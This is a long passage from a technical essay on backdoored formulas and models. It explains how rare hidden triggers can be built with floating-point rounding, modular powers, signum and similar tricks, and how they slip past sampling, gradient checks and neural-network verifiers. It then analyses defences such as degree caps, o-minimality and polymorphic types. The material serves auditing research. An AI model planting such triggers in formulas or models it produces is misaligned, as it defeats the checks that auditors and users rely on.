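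He also built exact tests for single values. He divided the numbers from −1 up to 1 into 256 equal intervals, one for each possible byte. One of his expressions gives 1/128 in the interval for 249 and 0 in all the others. In exact arithmetic it is a constant, because all the x's cancel. He found such expressions by computer search, and most of them are very long.

With a test for every byte value, Tom 7 could reproduce any table of bytes, and he used this to build a pseudorandom generator from addition and multiplication by constants. Equivalent integer code passed a suite of 106 statistical tests. The rounding version produces about 26 bytes a second, which is too slow to be a practical way to conceal a hash, but it shows that even hash-like mixing can return through rounding.

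Hwang, Lee and colleagues (2025) prove the general result in *Floating-Point Neural Networks Are Provably Robust Universal Approximators*. For any floating-point program that always halts, accepts finite numbers and returns numbers (possibly infinite ones), some fixed sequence of floating-point additions and multiplications, with constants, computes exactly the same outputs. This covers programs with loops and if-then-else, and it holds for nearly all practical number formats.

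The proof first uses rounding to map all inputs up to some threshold to one number, and all larger inputs to the next representable number. Further steps widen the gap between these two numbers, which gives a comparison with the threshold. Comparisons can be combined into a test for any set of inputs, and a weighted sum of such tests reproduces any table of outputs.

A designer therefore can't shrink the closure of a floating-point grammar by banning operations if the grammar keeps addition, multiplication and constants. Only limits on size, constants or the arithmetic itself can exclude anything. The general construction is enormous because it may need tests for a vast number of input sets and output values, but a single trigger doesn't need it, as the 29-symbol formula shows.

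An auditor might look for hidden steps by checking a model's slope instead of its outputs. Software usually calculates slopes by automatic differentiation, which applies the rules of calculus to each operation in turn and ignores rounding. For the 29-symbol formula, it therefore gives a slope of 3 at every x, including a, just as it would for 3x + 2.

*Floating-Point Networks with Automatic Differentiation Can Represent Almost All Floating-Point Functions* (Park, Park and Hwang, 2026) proves that for nearly any table of outputs and nearly any table of slopes, some floating-point neural network computes both. A network could therefore perform a task correctly while its computed slope is zero for every input. This couldn't happen in exact arithmetic, because a differentiable function determines its own slope. The theorem covers common activation functions and formats from 8 to 64 bits.

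### Guarantees for the wrong arithmetic

Verification software tries to prove that a neural network behaves properly on every input in some region. A verifier is sound if everything it certifies is true. *Exploiting Verified Neural Networks via Floating Point Numerical Error* (Jia and Rinard, 2020) showed that many verifiers of the time were unsound because they treated floating-point numbers as real numbers. Jia and Rinard found inputs on which networks violated properties that a verifier had certified.

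More careful verifiers track their own rounding errors, so that their bounds contain the network's exact output. In *No Soundness in the Real World*, Szász, Bánhelyi and Jelasity (2025) prove that a verifier can be sound for the exact network and still be wrong about the rounded one that users run. They also tested well-known verifiers on networks built to behave differently depending on details of the computer system, such as the precision or the order of additions. Every verifier failed to bound the deployed networks' outputs correctly.

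The order of the terms matters because floating-point addition isn't associative. In double precision, 2⁵³ + 1 − 2⁵³ gives 0 from left to right, because 2⁵³ + 1 isn't representable and rounds to 2⁵³. The reordered sum 2⁵³ − 2⁵³ + 1 gives 1. Systems that split a long sum among many processors may add the terms in a different order on each run, so even the same machine doesn't always compute the same function.

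A short formula on a single processor largely avoids this last problem, since its author can fix the order of operations with brackets. But anyone who rearranges the formula to simplify it, or proves something about it in exact algebra, makes the same substitution as the verifiers.

### Testing the defences

A grammar designer can require every intermediate result to be a real number. This rules out Odrzywołek's constructions and the floor formula based on complex logarithms. Real exponentials, real logarithms and arithmetic form an o-minimal structure, so no formula built from them can have infinitely many jumps, as the floor function does. These operations can still produce a single spike. For any nonzero x, e^(½·ln(x·x)) is the absolute value of x, which can be used to compute the maximum, and on whole numbers max(1 − |x − a|, 0) tests whether x equals a. If the grammar also has tangent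 and arctangent, formulas can round without using complex numbers.

Fixed-point arithmetic removes some of the tricks that depend on rounding. It stores every number as a whole multiple of one unit, such as 0.001, so addition is exact as long as the result fits. Then (x + 2⁵²) − 2⁵² equals x, and the order of additions doesn't matter. Szász and colleagues mention fixed-point arithmetic as a promising alternative because its rounding errors have a known limit, which a verifier can take into account.

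Multiplication still has to round, however. With a unit of 0.001 and rounding down, consider

(x·0.001)·1000

If a computer keeps three decimal places and drops the rest, multiplying a non-negative x by 0.001 and then by 1000 computes the floor function. For x = 3.217, the first product is 0.003217, which the computer stores as 0.003, and the second is 3. Addition can also compute a banned operation when the result is too large to store. It computes a remainder if the result wraps around, and a minimum if the result is capped at the largest allowed value. To exclude these operations completely, the designer would need exact whole numbers or fractions with enough room for every intermediate result, and would have to give up exp, log and sine.

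Interval arithmetic keeps the floating-point format but tracks the rounding error. It replaces each number with a lower and an upper bound, rounding the lower one down and the upper one up, so the exact result always lies between them. In the 29-symbol formula, each bracket becomes the interval from 0 to 1, whatever x is, and the output becomes the interval from 3x + 1 to 3x + 3. For the formula 3·x + 2, which hides no trigger, the two bounds are equal.

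Evaluating this formula once at a random input therefore exposes it without finding a, and so does running it with a different rounding direction, as in the table above. A wide interval doesn't prove that a trigger exists, because some formulas without one also subtract huge numbers that nearly cancel. Another formula might have a trigger and still give a narrow interval, if its rounding error becomes large only near a.

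Intervals also differ in what they are meant to contain. Hwang and colleagues note that the usual kind, which rounds outward, encloses the exact result of each operation. They use a kind that encloses the rounded results the computer produces. Intervals that round outward also contain the computer's result if it performs the same operations in the same order, but may not otherwise. For example, evaluating 2⁵³ − 2⁵³ + 1 from left to right gives the interval [1, 1], but a machine that computes 2⁵³ + 1 first returns 0.

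The most direct defence is to check the arithmetic that will run. With one 32-bit input, an auditor can try every value on the deployed program. For larger inputs, a solver can translate the floating-point operations, including rounding, into Boolean clauses (bit-blasting) and search for an input where the output differs from the reference. Jia and Rinard note that such solvers exist, but that researchers verifying neural networks used inexact arithmetic for speed. Exact checking is more realistic for a thirty-symbol formula because it has few operations, although multiplying the 53-bit significands of two double-precision numbers takes nearly 50,000 clauses by Brain's count.

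The result holds only for the arithmetic that the auditor checked. The auditor has to record the precision, the rounding direction, the order of operations, the compiler options and the library that computes functions such as exp and sin, since libraries can differ in the last digit. Turning on the compiler option that cancels 2⁵² − 2⁵² removes the trigger from the 29-symbol formula. The same change could add a trigger to a different formula, so the auditor has to repeat the check whenever any of these settings changes.

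## Numeric grammars that limit how rare a change can be

Banning individual operations fails if the remaining ones can rebuild them. A designer can instead restrict a property of the whole function, such as its degree or steepest slope. For some of these properties, a theorem limits how rarely two different models from the same grammar can disagree. Sampling can then test whether a model is exactly 3x + 2, because any other model in the grammar gives a different output on at least a known share of inputs. The theorems assume exact arithmetic, so they don't cover triggers caused by rounding.

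### Low degree on bits

The degree of a polynomial is the largest number of variables multiplied together in any one term, counting repeats. For example, x·x·y + 5 has degree 3. To find an upper limit on the degree without expanding the formula, an auditor can count each constant as 0 and each variable as 1, then take the larger of the two counts at each sum and add the two counts at each product.

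A 32-bit number x equals b₀ + 2b₁ + 4b₂ + … + 2³¹b₃₁, where each b is one of its bits. This sum has degree 1 in the bits, so a polynomial of degree d in x has degree at most d in the bits. Two different functions of degree at most d in the bits differ on at least 1/2^d of all n-bit inputs, for any n. To prove this, let P be their difference. P is nonzero on some input, and we can write it so that no term contains the same bit twice, because a bit squared equals itself.

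1. If there are no bits at all, P is a nonzero constant and the claim holds. Otherwise, assume that it holds for functions with one bit fewer.
2. Pick a bit b and write P = b·A + B, where A and B use only the other bits. A has degree at most d − 1.
3. When b = 0, P equals B. When b = 1, P equals A + B. Each case covers half the inputs.
4. If B and A + B are both nonzero somewhere, each is nonzero on at least 1/2^d of its half, so P is nonzero on at least 1/2^d of all inputs.
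5. If one of them is 0 everywhere, the other is A or −A. Its degree is at most d − 1, so it is nonzero on at least 1/2^(d−1) of its half, which is again 1/2^d of all inputs.

The product b₀·b₁·b₂·b₃ has degree 4 and is nonzero on exactly 1/16 of inputs, so the bound is tight. The proof only adds and subtracts outputs, so *A Near-Optimal Polynomial Distance Lemma Over Boolean Slices* (Amireddy, Behera et al., 2025) states the result for any number system with ordinary addition and subtraction, including 32-bit arithmetic that wraps around at 2³².

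Suppose a grammar allows only polynomials of degree at most 4. Any model other than 3x + 2 then differs from it on at least one input in 16, so 100 random draws would all miss the difference at most about 0.16% of the time. Adding input variables doesn't weaken this guarantee.

A degree cap also rules out Thomas Read's disguised formula. Every operation in that formula receives common values, yet the formula differs from a simpler one on only one of the 2^n inputs. The four-bit version differs from x₄x₃ by x₁x₂x₃(1 − x₄), which has degree 4. The n-bit version differs by a polynomial of degree n, so rewriting the formula cannot bring it under a low cap.

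The guarantee depends on the inputs being uniformly random. For example, b₀ − b₁ has degree 1 but is almost always 0 if the first two bits of real inputs almost always match. Amireddy and colleagues study a milder departure from uniform inputs, in which exactly k of the n bits are on. They prove that, for low degrees and k at most half of n, the guaranteed share falls from 1/2^d to about (k/n)^d. If each input has exactly 100 of 1,000 yes-or-no features on, two models of degree 3 can differ on as few as one input in about 1,000, compared with one in 8 for free bits. *Low-Degree Testing Over Boolean Slices* (2026) derives a similar bound for inputs that combine free bits with a block in which exactly half the bits are on.

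### The Schwartz-Zippel lemma and its loophole

The guarantee is much stronger when each variable can take many values and the arithmetic is done in a finite field. The simplest finite fields consist of the numbers from 0 to p − 1 for a prime p, where each result is replaced by its remainder after division by p. The Schwartz-Zippel lemma says that two different polynomials of degree at most d over a field of q elements agree on at most a fraction d/q of inputs. Many modern error-correcting codes depend on this fact, according to *New Techniques for Constructing Rare-Case Hard Functions* (2024). Øystein Ore proved a version in 1922, and several people rediscovered it around 1980, so the lemma has several names. *The Curious History of the Schwartz-Zippel Lemma* (2009) lists them.

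With one variable, the lemma is the rule that a polynomial of degree d has at most d roots. If r is a root of P, then P = (x − r)·Q, where Q has degree d − 1. Any other root s makes (s − r)·Q(s) equal 0. In a field, a product is 0 only if one of its factors is, and s − r is not 0, so s is a root of Q. Factoring out each root lowers the degree by one, so P has at most d roots. The rule about products fails in arithmetic that wraps around at 2³², where 65,536·65,536 is 0 and x² has 65,536 roots.

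For p = 2³¹ − 1, two different polynomials of degree 4 agree on at most 4 of the 2,147,483,647 possible inputs, so testing one random input would almost certainly detect any model that differs from the reference.

However, the bound d/q says little once d gets close to q. By Fermat's little theorem, z^(p−1) leaves remainder 1 on division by p unless z is 0. For p = 7 and z = 3, for instance, 3⁶ = 729 = 7·104 + 1. So

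1 − (x − a)^(p−1)

is 1 when x = a and 0 for every other x. Bishnoi, Clark and colleagues (2015), in *On Zeros of a Polynomial in a Finite Grid*, call the underlying idea "Chevalley's trick". It is an exact equality test that uses nothing but subtraction and a power.

The test also takes few multiplications. For p = 2³¹ − 1, the exponent p − 1 is 2,147,483,646, which in binary is thirty ones followed by a zero. A program can compute the power in 59 multiplications by starting with x − a, squaring 30 times, and multiplying by x − a after each of the first 29 squarings. With a power operator, the whole model 3·x + 3 − (x − a)^(p−1) has size 11.

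A grammar without powers is still unsafe if it has squaring. The number 65,537 is prime and equals 2¹⁶ + 1, so squaring x − a sixteen times raises it to the required power, 65,536. Modulo 65,537, a formula of size 25 can therefore equal 3x + 2 on every input but one. With only addition, subtraction and multiplication, a pure formula of at most 30 symbols has at most 15 variable occurrences, so its degree is at most 15. But squaring, powers and named intermediate results each let the degree grow exponentially with length, so a designer should cap the degree itself.

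A theorem by Alon and Füredi, which Bishnoi and colleagues generalize, gives the exact trade-off for exact arithmetic on ordinary numbers. If a model reads four bytes, each a number from 0 to 255, two different polynomials must differ on at least this share of inputs:

| Degree cap | Smallest possible share of inputs that differ |
|---|---|
| 4 | 98% |
| 128 | 50% |
| 255 | 1 in 256 |
| 300 | 1 in 311 |
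| 510 | 1 in 65,536 |
| 1,020 | 1 in 4.3 billion |

A difference at a single input needs degree 1,020, or 255 for each byte. With a lower cap, a one-input trigger is impossible.

### The Remez inequality

"Differ" in these results means the outputs aren't exactly equal. On real numbers, a polynomial could in principle stay within a billionth of 3x + 2 nearly everywhere but differ from it by 1 in a narrow region. A tester who ignores tiny differences would miss the larger one.

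The Remez inequality, from 1936, limits this. Let P be the difference between a model and its reference, both polynomials of degree at most d, on an interval. Suppose that P stays within ±η except on a share ε of the interval. Then everywhere on the interval, including the exceptional part,

|P| ≤ η · T_d((1 + ε)/(1 − ε))

Here T_d is the Chebyshev polynomial of degree d. Of all degree-d polynomials that stay between −1 and 1 on the interval from −1 to 1, it grows fastest outside that interval. For d = 1, 2 and 3, it is x, 2x² − 1 and 4x³ − 3x. In this formula, T_d equals (r^d + r^(−d))/2, with r = (1 + √ε)/(1 − √ε).

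Take degree 10 and ε = 1%. Then √ε is 0.1, r is 1.1/0.9 or about 1.222, and r¹⁰ is about 7.44. The factor is (7.44 + 0.13)/2, or about 3.8. A difference that stays within 0.001 on 99% of the interval therefore can't exceed 0.0038 anywhere. The table gives the factor for other cases:

| Degree | ε = 1 in 100 | ε = 1 in 10,000 | ε = 1 in a million |
|---|---|---|---|
| 4 | 1.34 | 1.003 | 1.00003 |
| 10 | 3.8 | 1.02 | 1.0002 |
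| 100 | 260 million | 3.8 | 1.02 |
| 1,000 | 7 × 10⁸⁶ | 240 million | 3.8 |

This lets sampling limit the size of a departure that no draw has hit. If 30,000 random inputs all show differences within 0.001, the auditor can be 95% confident that ε is below 1 in 10,000. For models of degree at most 10, the difference is then at most 0.00102 everywhere.

A polynomial needs a degree of about 3.8/√ε to depart by 1 in a region covering a fraction ε of the interval while staying within 0.001 elsewhere. The degree is about 3,800 if the region covers one millionth of the interval and about 249,000 if it covers 1/2³².

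Slote, Volberg and Zhang (2023), in *A Dimension-Free Remez-Type Inequality on the Polytorus*, quote a common simplification of the inequality with the factor (4/(1 − ε))^d. For degree 10 and ε = 1%, this factor is about 1.2 million, while the exact form gives 3.8.

Limiting the number of terms doesn't replace a degree cap. On the interval from 0 to 1, the single term x^1000 exceeds one half only on the last 0.07%. *Norming Sets and Related Remez-type Inequalities* (Brudnyi and Yomdin, 2013) proves a Remez-type inequality for polynomials with few terms, in which the bound depends less on the share ε when there are fewer terms. But on an interval from *a* to *b*, the bound also contains (*b*/*a*)^*N*, where *N* is the highest power, so it becomes useless as *a* approaches 0.

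The grammar must also exclude division. The bump 1/(1 + K·(x − a)²) is a ratio of polynomials of degree at most 2, yet a large enough K makes it arbitrarily narrow.

### More inputs, weaker bounds

Brudnyi and Yomdin also give the form for n inputs, which Yuri Brudnyi and Ganzburg proved. It replaces ε with ε^(1/n). With 20 inputs, a share of one in a million becomes 0.000001^(1/20), or about 0.50. The bound for a one-in-a-million region is then about the same as the one-input bound for a region covering half of an interval.

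| Degree | Factor for 1 input | Factor for 20 inputs |
|---|---|---|
| 2 | 1.00001 | 17 |
| 4 | 1.00003 | 585 |
| 10 | 1.0002 | 23 million |

If two quadratic models with 20 inputs differ by no more than 0.001 on each of three million draws, they are guaranteed to differ by less than 0.02 everywhere. With degree-10 models, the difference could be as large as 23,000 after the same test.

Slote and colleagues explain why no proof can remove the dependence on dimension. Their example is the degree-2 polynomial 1 − (x₁² + x₂² + … + x_n²) on the ball of radius 1. It equals 1 at the centre, but in high dimensions nearly all of the ball's volume is close to its surface, where the polynomial is close to 0. With 64 inputs, it exceeds one half only within a distance of √½ from the centre, a region that fills (√½)⁶⁴ = 1/2³² of the ball.

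A quadratic can have a departure as rare as a match in an equality test on a 32-bit number, but the departure is far easier to find because it fades gradually. The average value over the ball is about 0.03, and a tester who looks for departures above 0.1 needs about 29 draws to find one.

For some grammars, an auditor can avoid the problem by choosing the test points carefully. Suppose no term contains the same variable twice, as in x·y·z + 2x − y. The function is then linear in each variable when the others are fixed, so its largest and smallest values on a box are at corners. With 20 inputs, the box has 1,048,576 corners, and evaluating the difference at all of them gives an exact bound for the whole box. Slote and colleagues prove a related result for polynomials in complex variables, where checking a fixed grid bounds the function to within a factor that depends on the degree and the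 grid spacing but not on the number of variables. Both methods are practical only for a small number of inputs, because the number of points to check grows exponentially with the number of variables.

Similar bounds exist for smooth functions that aren't polynomials. *Time-iteration methods for controllability* (2026) bounds such a function by a factor of roughly (8e·n/(1 − ε))^k, where n is the number of inputs and k is any degree the user picks, plus a term for how far the function is from a polynomial of degree k. With 20 inputs and k = 2, the factor is already about 190,000.

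### Bounded slope

A degree cap also limits how steep a polynomial can be. By a classical inequality of Markov, a polynomial of degree d that stays between −1 and 1 on the interval from −1 to 1 has slope at most d² there. A designer could cap the slope directly and allow other functions too, including max, absolute value and tanh. Slope limits are easy to calculate from a formula because they add when two parts are added and multiply when one function goes inside another.

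Suppose two models have slope at most L and differ by h at some point c. The gap between them shrinks by at most 2L per unit of distance from c, so they still differ at every point less than h/(2L) from c. These points span a width of h/L, unless c is near the end of the range. For example, if L = 5, h = 1 and inputs lie between 0 and 1, the models differ on at least a fifth of inputs, or at least a tenth if c is close to one end.

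With more inputs, let the slope be the change in output divided by the largest change in any single input. The models then differ throughout a box with sides of length h/L. For sides of 0.2, the box's share of all inputs shrinks quickly:

| Inputs | Share of the unit cube |
|---|---|
| 1 | 20% |
| 2 | 4% |
| 5 | 1 in 3,125 |
| 10 | 1 in 9.8 million |
| 20 | 1 in 95 trillion |

With 20 inputs, the share is about 10⁻¹⁴. To guarantee a one-in-a-million share, the box would need sides of about 0.5, so the slope limit for a departure of 1 would have to be about 2. If all inputs were between 0 and 1, the output of a model with this limit could change by at most 2 across the whole cube.

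A better option is to limit how many input variables a formula uses. If the model and its reference together use only three of the 20 variables, their difference depends only on those three. A box with sides of 0.2 in those variables then covers 0.2³, or 0.8%, of the input space.

Slope limits restrict rare changes much less on whole numbers, where neighbouring inputs are a full unit apart. The running example, 3·x + 2 + (x = a), rises by 4 from a − 1 to a, by 2 from a to a + 1, and by 3 everywhere else. On whole numbers, max(1 − |x − a|, 0) equals the test (x = a) and has slope 1, so a grammar with a limit of 5 would allow the trigger. Only departures much larger than the limit have to affect many inputs. For example, a departure of a million under a limit of 10 affects at least about 100,000 of the 2³² inputs, or one in 43,000.

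### Monotonicity and other shape constraints

People who fit formulas to data often know something about the shape the formula should have. For example, a dose-response curve shouldn't fall as the dose rises, and a cost shouldn't be negative. In shape-constrained symbolic regression, the user states such facts as constraints, and the software rejects or penalizes formulas that violate them. Typical constraints require the output to rise with a given input, stay between two limits, or curve in one direction.

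Monotonicity, meaning that the output never falls as the input rises, gives a guarantee like the one for slope. Suppose the reference is 3x + 2 and a monotone model exceeds it by h at x = a. Because the model's output can't fall, it stays above the reference until 3x + 2 reaches the same value, h/3 units later. A departure of 300 on whole numbers therefore affects at least 100 inputs, unless the range ends first. This holds however steep the model is, even if it contains jumps.

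A monotone model can still have a lone exception at a if the new output fits between the reference's outputs at a − 1 and a + 1. For example, the outputs of 3·x + 2 + (x = a) at a − 1, a and a + 1 are 3a − 1, 3a + 3 and 3a + 5, which still increase. If the inputs are yes-or-no features, monotonicity doesn't limit how rare an exception can be. An "and" of 32 features is monotone, and it is true for only one input in 2³².

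Convexity, which requires the slope never to fall, is stricter. If a convex model matches a straight line at several points on both sides of a, it has to match at a too, so it can't hide a lone exception in the middle of the range. It can hide one at the end:

3·x + 2 + max(x − 4,294,967,294, 0)

For 32-bit whole numbers, this function equals 3x + 2 except at the largest input, where it is 1 higher. It is monotone and convex, and its slope is never above 4. A tester who tries the extreme inputs would find the exception at once, but one who samples inputs at random almost certainly wouldn't.

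Output limits restrict how large a departure can be, but not how rare it can be. They do reduce the harm a departure can do, which may matter more to the user than its rarity.

The guarantees hold only if the software checks the constraint over the whole range. A check at sampled points can miss a narrow violation, just as sampling can miss a trigger. A common alternative is to calculate the formula's derivative and bound it with interval arithmetic, but this can reject good formulas. For example, x³/3 − x² + x never falls, because its derivative is (x − 1)². If the derivative is written as x² − 2x + 1, interval arithmetic on inputs from 0 to 2 gives bounds of −3 and 5, which don't confirm that it is never negative. The check can also accept bad formulas if the grammar has comparisons or floors, because their derivatives are 0 everywhere except at the jumps, so the software has to treat those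 operations separately.

### O-minimal grammars

O-minimality restricts how complicated a function can be without limiting its degree or slope. An o-minimal structure on the real numbers includes every set that polynomial equations and inequalities define. It is closed under "and", "or", "not" and "there exists", and every set of real numbers in it is a finite union of points and intervals.

The last condition excludes unrestricted sine. It also excludes the floor function, because ⌊x⌋ = x has infinitely many isolated solutions. The grammar can still include polynomials, roots, max, comparisons, exponentials, logarithms, tanh, and sine on a bounded range.

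Karpinski and Macintyre explain a further theorem in *Polynomial Bounds for VC Dimension of Sigmoidal Neural Networks*. When the condition holds, the number of separate pieces in the set a formula defines has a limit that doesn't depend on the formula's adjustable constants. In the bump model 3·x + 2 + 1/(1 + K·(x − a)²), the output differs from 3·x + 2 by more than one half on only one interval, whatever K and a are. Someone writing the formula can't turn one exception into a thousand by choosing the digits of the constants, as they can with a sine's frequency. But the theorem doesn't limit how narrow the interval is, and a piece can be a single point.

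Limiting the number of pieces also limits the VC dimension. Karpinski and Macintyre credit Laskowski with the general theorem that, in an o-minimal structure, every family of sets defined by one formula with adjustable constants has finite VC dimension. His proof gives no realistic estimate of that dimension, but they provide one, roughly 2·log B + 17·ℓ·log s. Here B is a limit on the number of pieces, ℓ is the number of adjustable constants, s is the number of expressions that the formula compares with 0, and the logarithms are to base 2. For two polynomials of degree 4 and five constants, the estimate is somewhat over 100.

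Johnson and Laskowski (2009) give a more precise count of the patterns in *Compression schemes, stable definable families, and o-minimal structures*. On N points, a formula with m adjustable constants can produce at most about N^m of the 2^N possible yes-or-no patterns. They prove that the whole pattern can be reconstructed from at most m of the points and a fixed amount of extra information. For intervals on a line, for example, the leftmost and rightmost points inside the interval determine the answers for all the others. The result also covers sums such as a₁x^b₁ + a₂x^b₂ for positive x, where the exponents are adjustable too.

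*On Sample Complexity of Neural Networks* (Usvyatsov, 2019) uses this count to show that the number of examples needed to measure a network's accuracy grows almost in proportion to its number of weights. For many networks, the older VC bounds grew at least as fast as the square of the number of weights.

Kratsios, Cousins and colleagues (2026), in *Every Feedforward Neural Network Definable in an o-Minimal Structure Has Finite Sample Complexity*, extended the approach to nearly all standard network designs without loops, including transformers with a fixed input length. A formula with a fixed layout and adjustable constants is a small network of this kind. For yes-or-no outputs, their theorem says that

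N ≥ C·(K + log(1/δ))/t²

random examples are enough. With probability at least 1 − δ, the accuracy on those examples is then within t of the true accuracy for every choice of constants at once. K depends on the formula's layout but not on the size of its constants, so even K = 10¹² in a bump gets no special treatment.

The proof uses the fact that any fixed combination of operations from an o-minimal structure also belongs to that structure. The family therefore has finite VC dimension, and standard results then give a sufficient number of examples. Like Yarotsky, Kratsios and colleagues have to restrict sine by bounding both its input range and any adjustable frequency. They don't calculate sharp values for the constants C and K, and the theorem covers only one fixed layout at a time.

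The theorem guarantees that a sample measures ε to within a tolerance t. A trigger at one 32-bit input has ε = 1/2³². To distinguish that from 0, an auditor would need t below 1/2³², which makes 1/t² more than 2⁶⁴. Trying all 2³² inputs would be far quicker.

O-minimality can help a solver more than a sampler. If the grammar has only arithmetic and comparisons on real numbers, Tarski's decision method can always determine whether a model differs from its reference, though it may take too long to be practical. No method can always do this for the same operations on whole numbers, because a model with enough inputs can add 1 whenever a polynomial equals 0, and determining whether that ever happens means solving Hilbert's tenth problem.

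### Rarity times VC dimension

In the attacker-and-defender game, where the trigger is random and the defender sees it, Christiano and colleagues prove that the best defender with unlimited computing time loses with probability roughly proportional to the VC dimension times ε, up to a maximum of one half. Such a defender can therefore win almost always if ε is much smaller than 1 divided by the VC dimension.

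To see why the attacker wins when ε is larger, suppose the VC dimension is 1,000. Some set of 1,000 inputs allows every pattern of yes and no answers. The attacker makes those inputs equally likely, chooses a random pattern as the original function, and flips the answer at the trigger, which is one input in 1,000. The result is another random pattern, so the defender cannot tell whether the function was changed.

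When ε is small, such as 1/2³² for a class with VC dimension 10, the defender can make repeated predictions and take a majority vote, as with efficiently learnable classes.

1. The defender draws about 2³⁰ labelled examples from the function they received. If it has a backdoor, the chance that any example falls on an altered input is at most 1/4.
2. A method by Haussler, Littlestone and Warmuth predicts the answer at the given input from these examples. Averaged over random inputs, its error rate is at most 10/2³⁰ if the examples are clean.
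3. The trigger is a random input too. By Markov's inequality, the chance that it is one of the inputs where the method errs more than 1/8 of the time is at most 80/2³⁰, or about 1 in 13 million.
4. For any other trigger, each prediction is wrong with probability at most 1/4 + 1/8. This is less than one half, so the majority vote is almost always right.

With enough repetitions, the defender loses less than once in ten million games. The defender doesn't read the formula, but needs billions of examples.

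A class with a small VC dimension can still contain triggers. The tests "x = a" have VC dimension 1, so a defender facing a random trigger nearly always wins, yet each test gives 0 on every input except one. These tests also belong to every o-minimal grammar, since a single point is a finite union of points and intervals. The formula "x = y₁ or x = y₂ or … or x = y_m" has m adjustable constants and can mark any m inputs as exceptions. Usvyatsov uses it to show that the limit of about N^m patterns is the best possible.

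## Programming languages that withhold equality tests

Caps on degree and slope suit models that calculate, but many programs mostly move data around, for example by reversing lists, merging records or passing messages along. A language designer can use a type system to stop such programs from examining the data at all. A type is a label such as "whole number" or "list of letters". Before the program runs, the compiler checks that every operation receives data of a type it can handle.

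A function is *parametrically polymorphic* if it works for every type and does the same thing for each. Reversing a list, for example, works the same way for numbers, names and photographs. The function's author writes X for the unknown type and can use only operations that exist for every type. The equality test (x = a) isn't one of them, because x might belong to a type that has no such test.

### Functions that can't inspect their input

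In *Formal Parametric Polymorphism*, Abadi, Cardelli and Curien give a short proof that a function f is constant if it accepts a value of any type and returns yes or no. The proof uses John Reynolds's principle that a polymorphic function given paired inputs must return paired outputs, whatever rule pairs the values of one type with those of another. Yes-or-no outputs count as paired only if they are equal. The proof pairs every value of a type A with the single value "yes", so for any a in A, f(a) must equal f(yes), which doesn't depend on a. An auditor who trusts the compiler can therefore rule out a trigger in f without reading its code.

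Wadler (1989), in *Theorems for free!*, derives a similar result for functions that turn a list of X into another list of X. If r is such a function and g is any function on single elements, applying g to every element and then running r gives the same list as running r first and then applying g to every element. Since r can't inspect the elements, it can only rearrange, copy or drop them. *Theorems for free for the unenlightened* gives the example of a function that turns "schooled" into "shoe", and so must turn "SCHOOLED" into "SHOE". This test doesn't show which "o" the function kept, but a test on eight different letters would determine what it does to every list of length eight.

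Suppose a program reverses a list of numbers unless the first is 2,718,281,828, in which case it returns the list unchanged. The function g adds 1 to each number, and the starting list is [2,718,281,827, 5, 6].

- Running the program and then adding 1 gives [7, 6, 2,718,281,828].
- Adding 1 and then running the program gives [2,718,281,828, 6, 7].

The results differ, so this program can't be polymorphic. The compiler will reject the program if its author declares that it works for lists of any type.

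### Declaring equality in the type

Wadler shows that nobody can write a general equality test in a purely polymorphic language. Such a test would have to give the same answer for x and y as for g(x) and g(y), whatever g is. But if x and y differ and g sends everything to 0, a correct test must return false for the first pair and true for the second.

Some languages have a built-in equality test for all types, as Miranda did in the 1980s and OCaml does today. A function's type then doesn't show whether the function compares its data, and Wadler's theorem can fail. Standard ML and Haskell require the programmer to declare equality in the type. In Haskell, "Eq X" in front of a function's type means that X can be any type with an equality test. The theorem then still holds if g is one-to-one, meaning it never turns different values into equal ones.

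With this declaration, an author can write a program that reverses a list unless its first two elements are equal. The author still can't mention 2,718,281,828, because X may not be a type of numbers. An auditor who sees the declaration therefore knows that a trigger can depend on which elements are equal, but not on their specific values.

Seidel and Voigtländer, in *Proving Properties About Functions on Lists Involving Element Tests*, make this exact for functions from lists to lists. Without any declaration, the list's length determines which input positions the output comes from. With equality, the choice can also depend on which positions hold equal elements, and with order comparisons, on how the elements rank. An auditor can test one list for each possible pattern:

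| Declared in the type | What the rearrangement can depend on | Tests that settle all lists of length 4 |
|---|---|---|
| nothing | length | 1 |
| equality | length, and which elements are equal | 15 |
| order | length, and the ranking, including ties | 75 |
| elements are 32-bit numbers | everything | 2¹²⁸ |

If four elements are random 32-bit numbers, the chance that they are all equal is 1 in 2⁹⁶. Sampling would almost certainly not find a trigger that requires all four to be equal, but the 15 tests include that case.

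### Harmless-looking declarations

*Five-Point Haskell* suggests reading a declaration such as "Show X" as an extra argument. The function also receives a way to turn an X into text, and this is its only way to inspect an X. But text has its own equality test, so a function with only "Show X" in its type can still test x against a constant by converting x to text and comparing the result with "2718281828".

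Arithmetic raises the same problem. A polymorphic function can't compute 3x + 2 unless it receives addition and multiplication. Suppose it receives only addition, subtraction, multiplication and whole-number constants. It must then compute a polynomial, and an auditor can find out which one by running it on the symbol t instead of a number. Degree limits then apply as before. However, Haskell's standard declaration for arithmetic, "Num X", also includes signum, which gives −1, 0 or 1 according to a number's sign. The formula

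3·x + 3 − signum(x − a)·signum(x − a)

is therefore the running example again, at size 15, with no "Eq" in its type. As with any grammar, what matters is the closure of the declared operations.

### How many values a checker has to try

In 1986, Pierre Wolper applied a related idea, data independence, to programs that may run forever, such as communication protocols. *On model checking data-independent systems with arrays without reset* (Lazić, Newcomb and Roscoe, 2004) defines a program as data-independent in a type if it only reads, stores, copies and outputs values of that type, and tests pairs of them for equality. Such a program can't compare a value with a constant or do arithmetic on it.

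A model checker explores every state a program can reach and tests whether a stated property always holds. With several 32-bit variables there are far too many states. For a data-independent program, however, the checker can often pretend that the type has only a few possible values, and the answer holds for every larger type. Lazić worked out how many values are enough, under some technical conditions:

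| Equality tests | Property to check | Possible values needed |
|---|---|---|
| none | doesn't concern the data, such as "never gets stuck" | 1 |
| none | concerns the data, such as "delivers messages in order" | 2 |
| allowed | concerns which outputs may occur | the number stored by the program, plus the number the property has to remember, plus the most the program takes in or picks arbitrarily in one step |

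Without equality tests, two data values are enough to test a program because the steps it takes can't depend on the data's values. Its only possible error is to deliver the wrong item, and marking one item 1 and all the others 0 exposes that error.

As an example with equality tests, suppose one program drops each item equal to the one before it, and a second program reads that output and keeps only items equal to the one before. Given 7, 7, 9, 9, 9, 7, the first program outputs 7, 9, 7 and the second outputs nothing. Checking the programs with only three possible item values is enough to prove that the second never outputs anything, even for 32-bit items. Each program stores one item, the property stores none, and the programs read one item at a time. Their behaviour at each step therefore depends only on which of three items are equal, and three values can produce every such combination.

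Checking a program on a type with few possible values quickly finds a trigger that requires matching values, because matches are common there, but it can miss a trigger that requires different values. If a program reads five values and misbehaves only when all five differ, a checker that allows four possible values will find nothing. The rule in the table correctly gives 5 as the number of possible values needed, because the program has to store four values when it reads the fifth.

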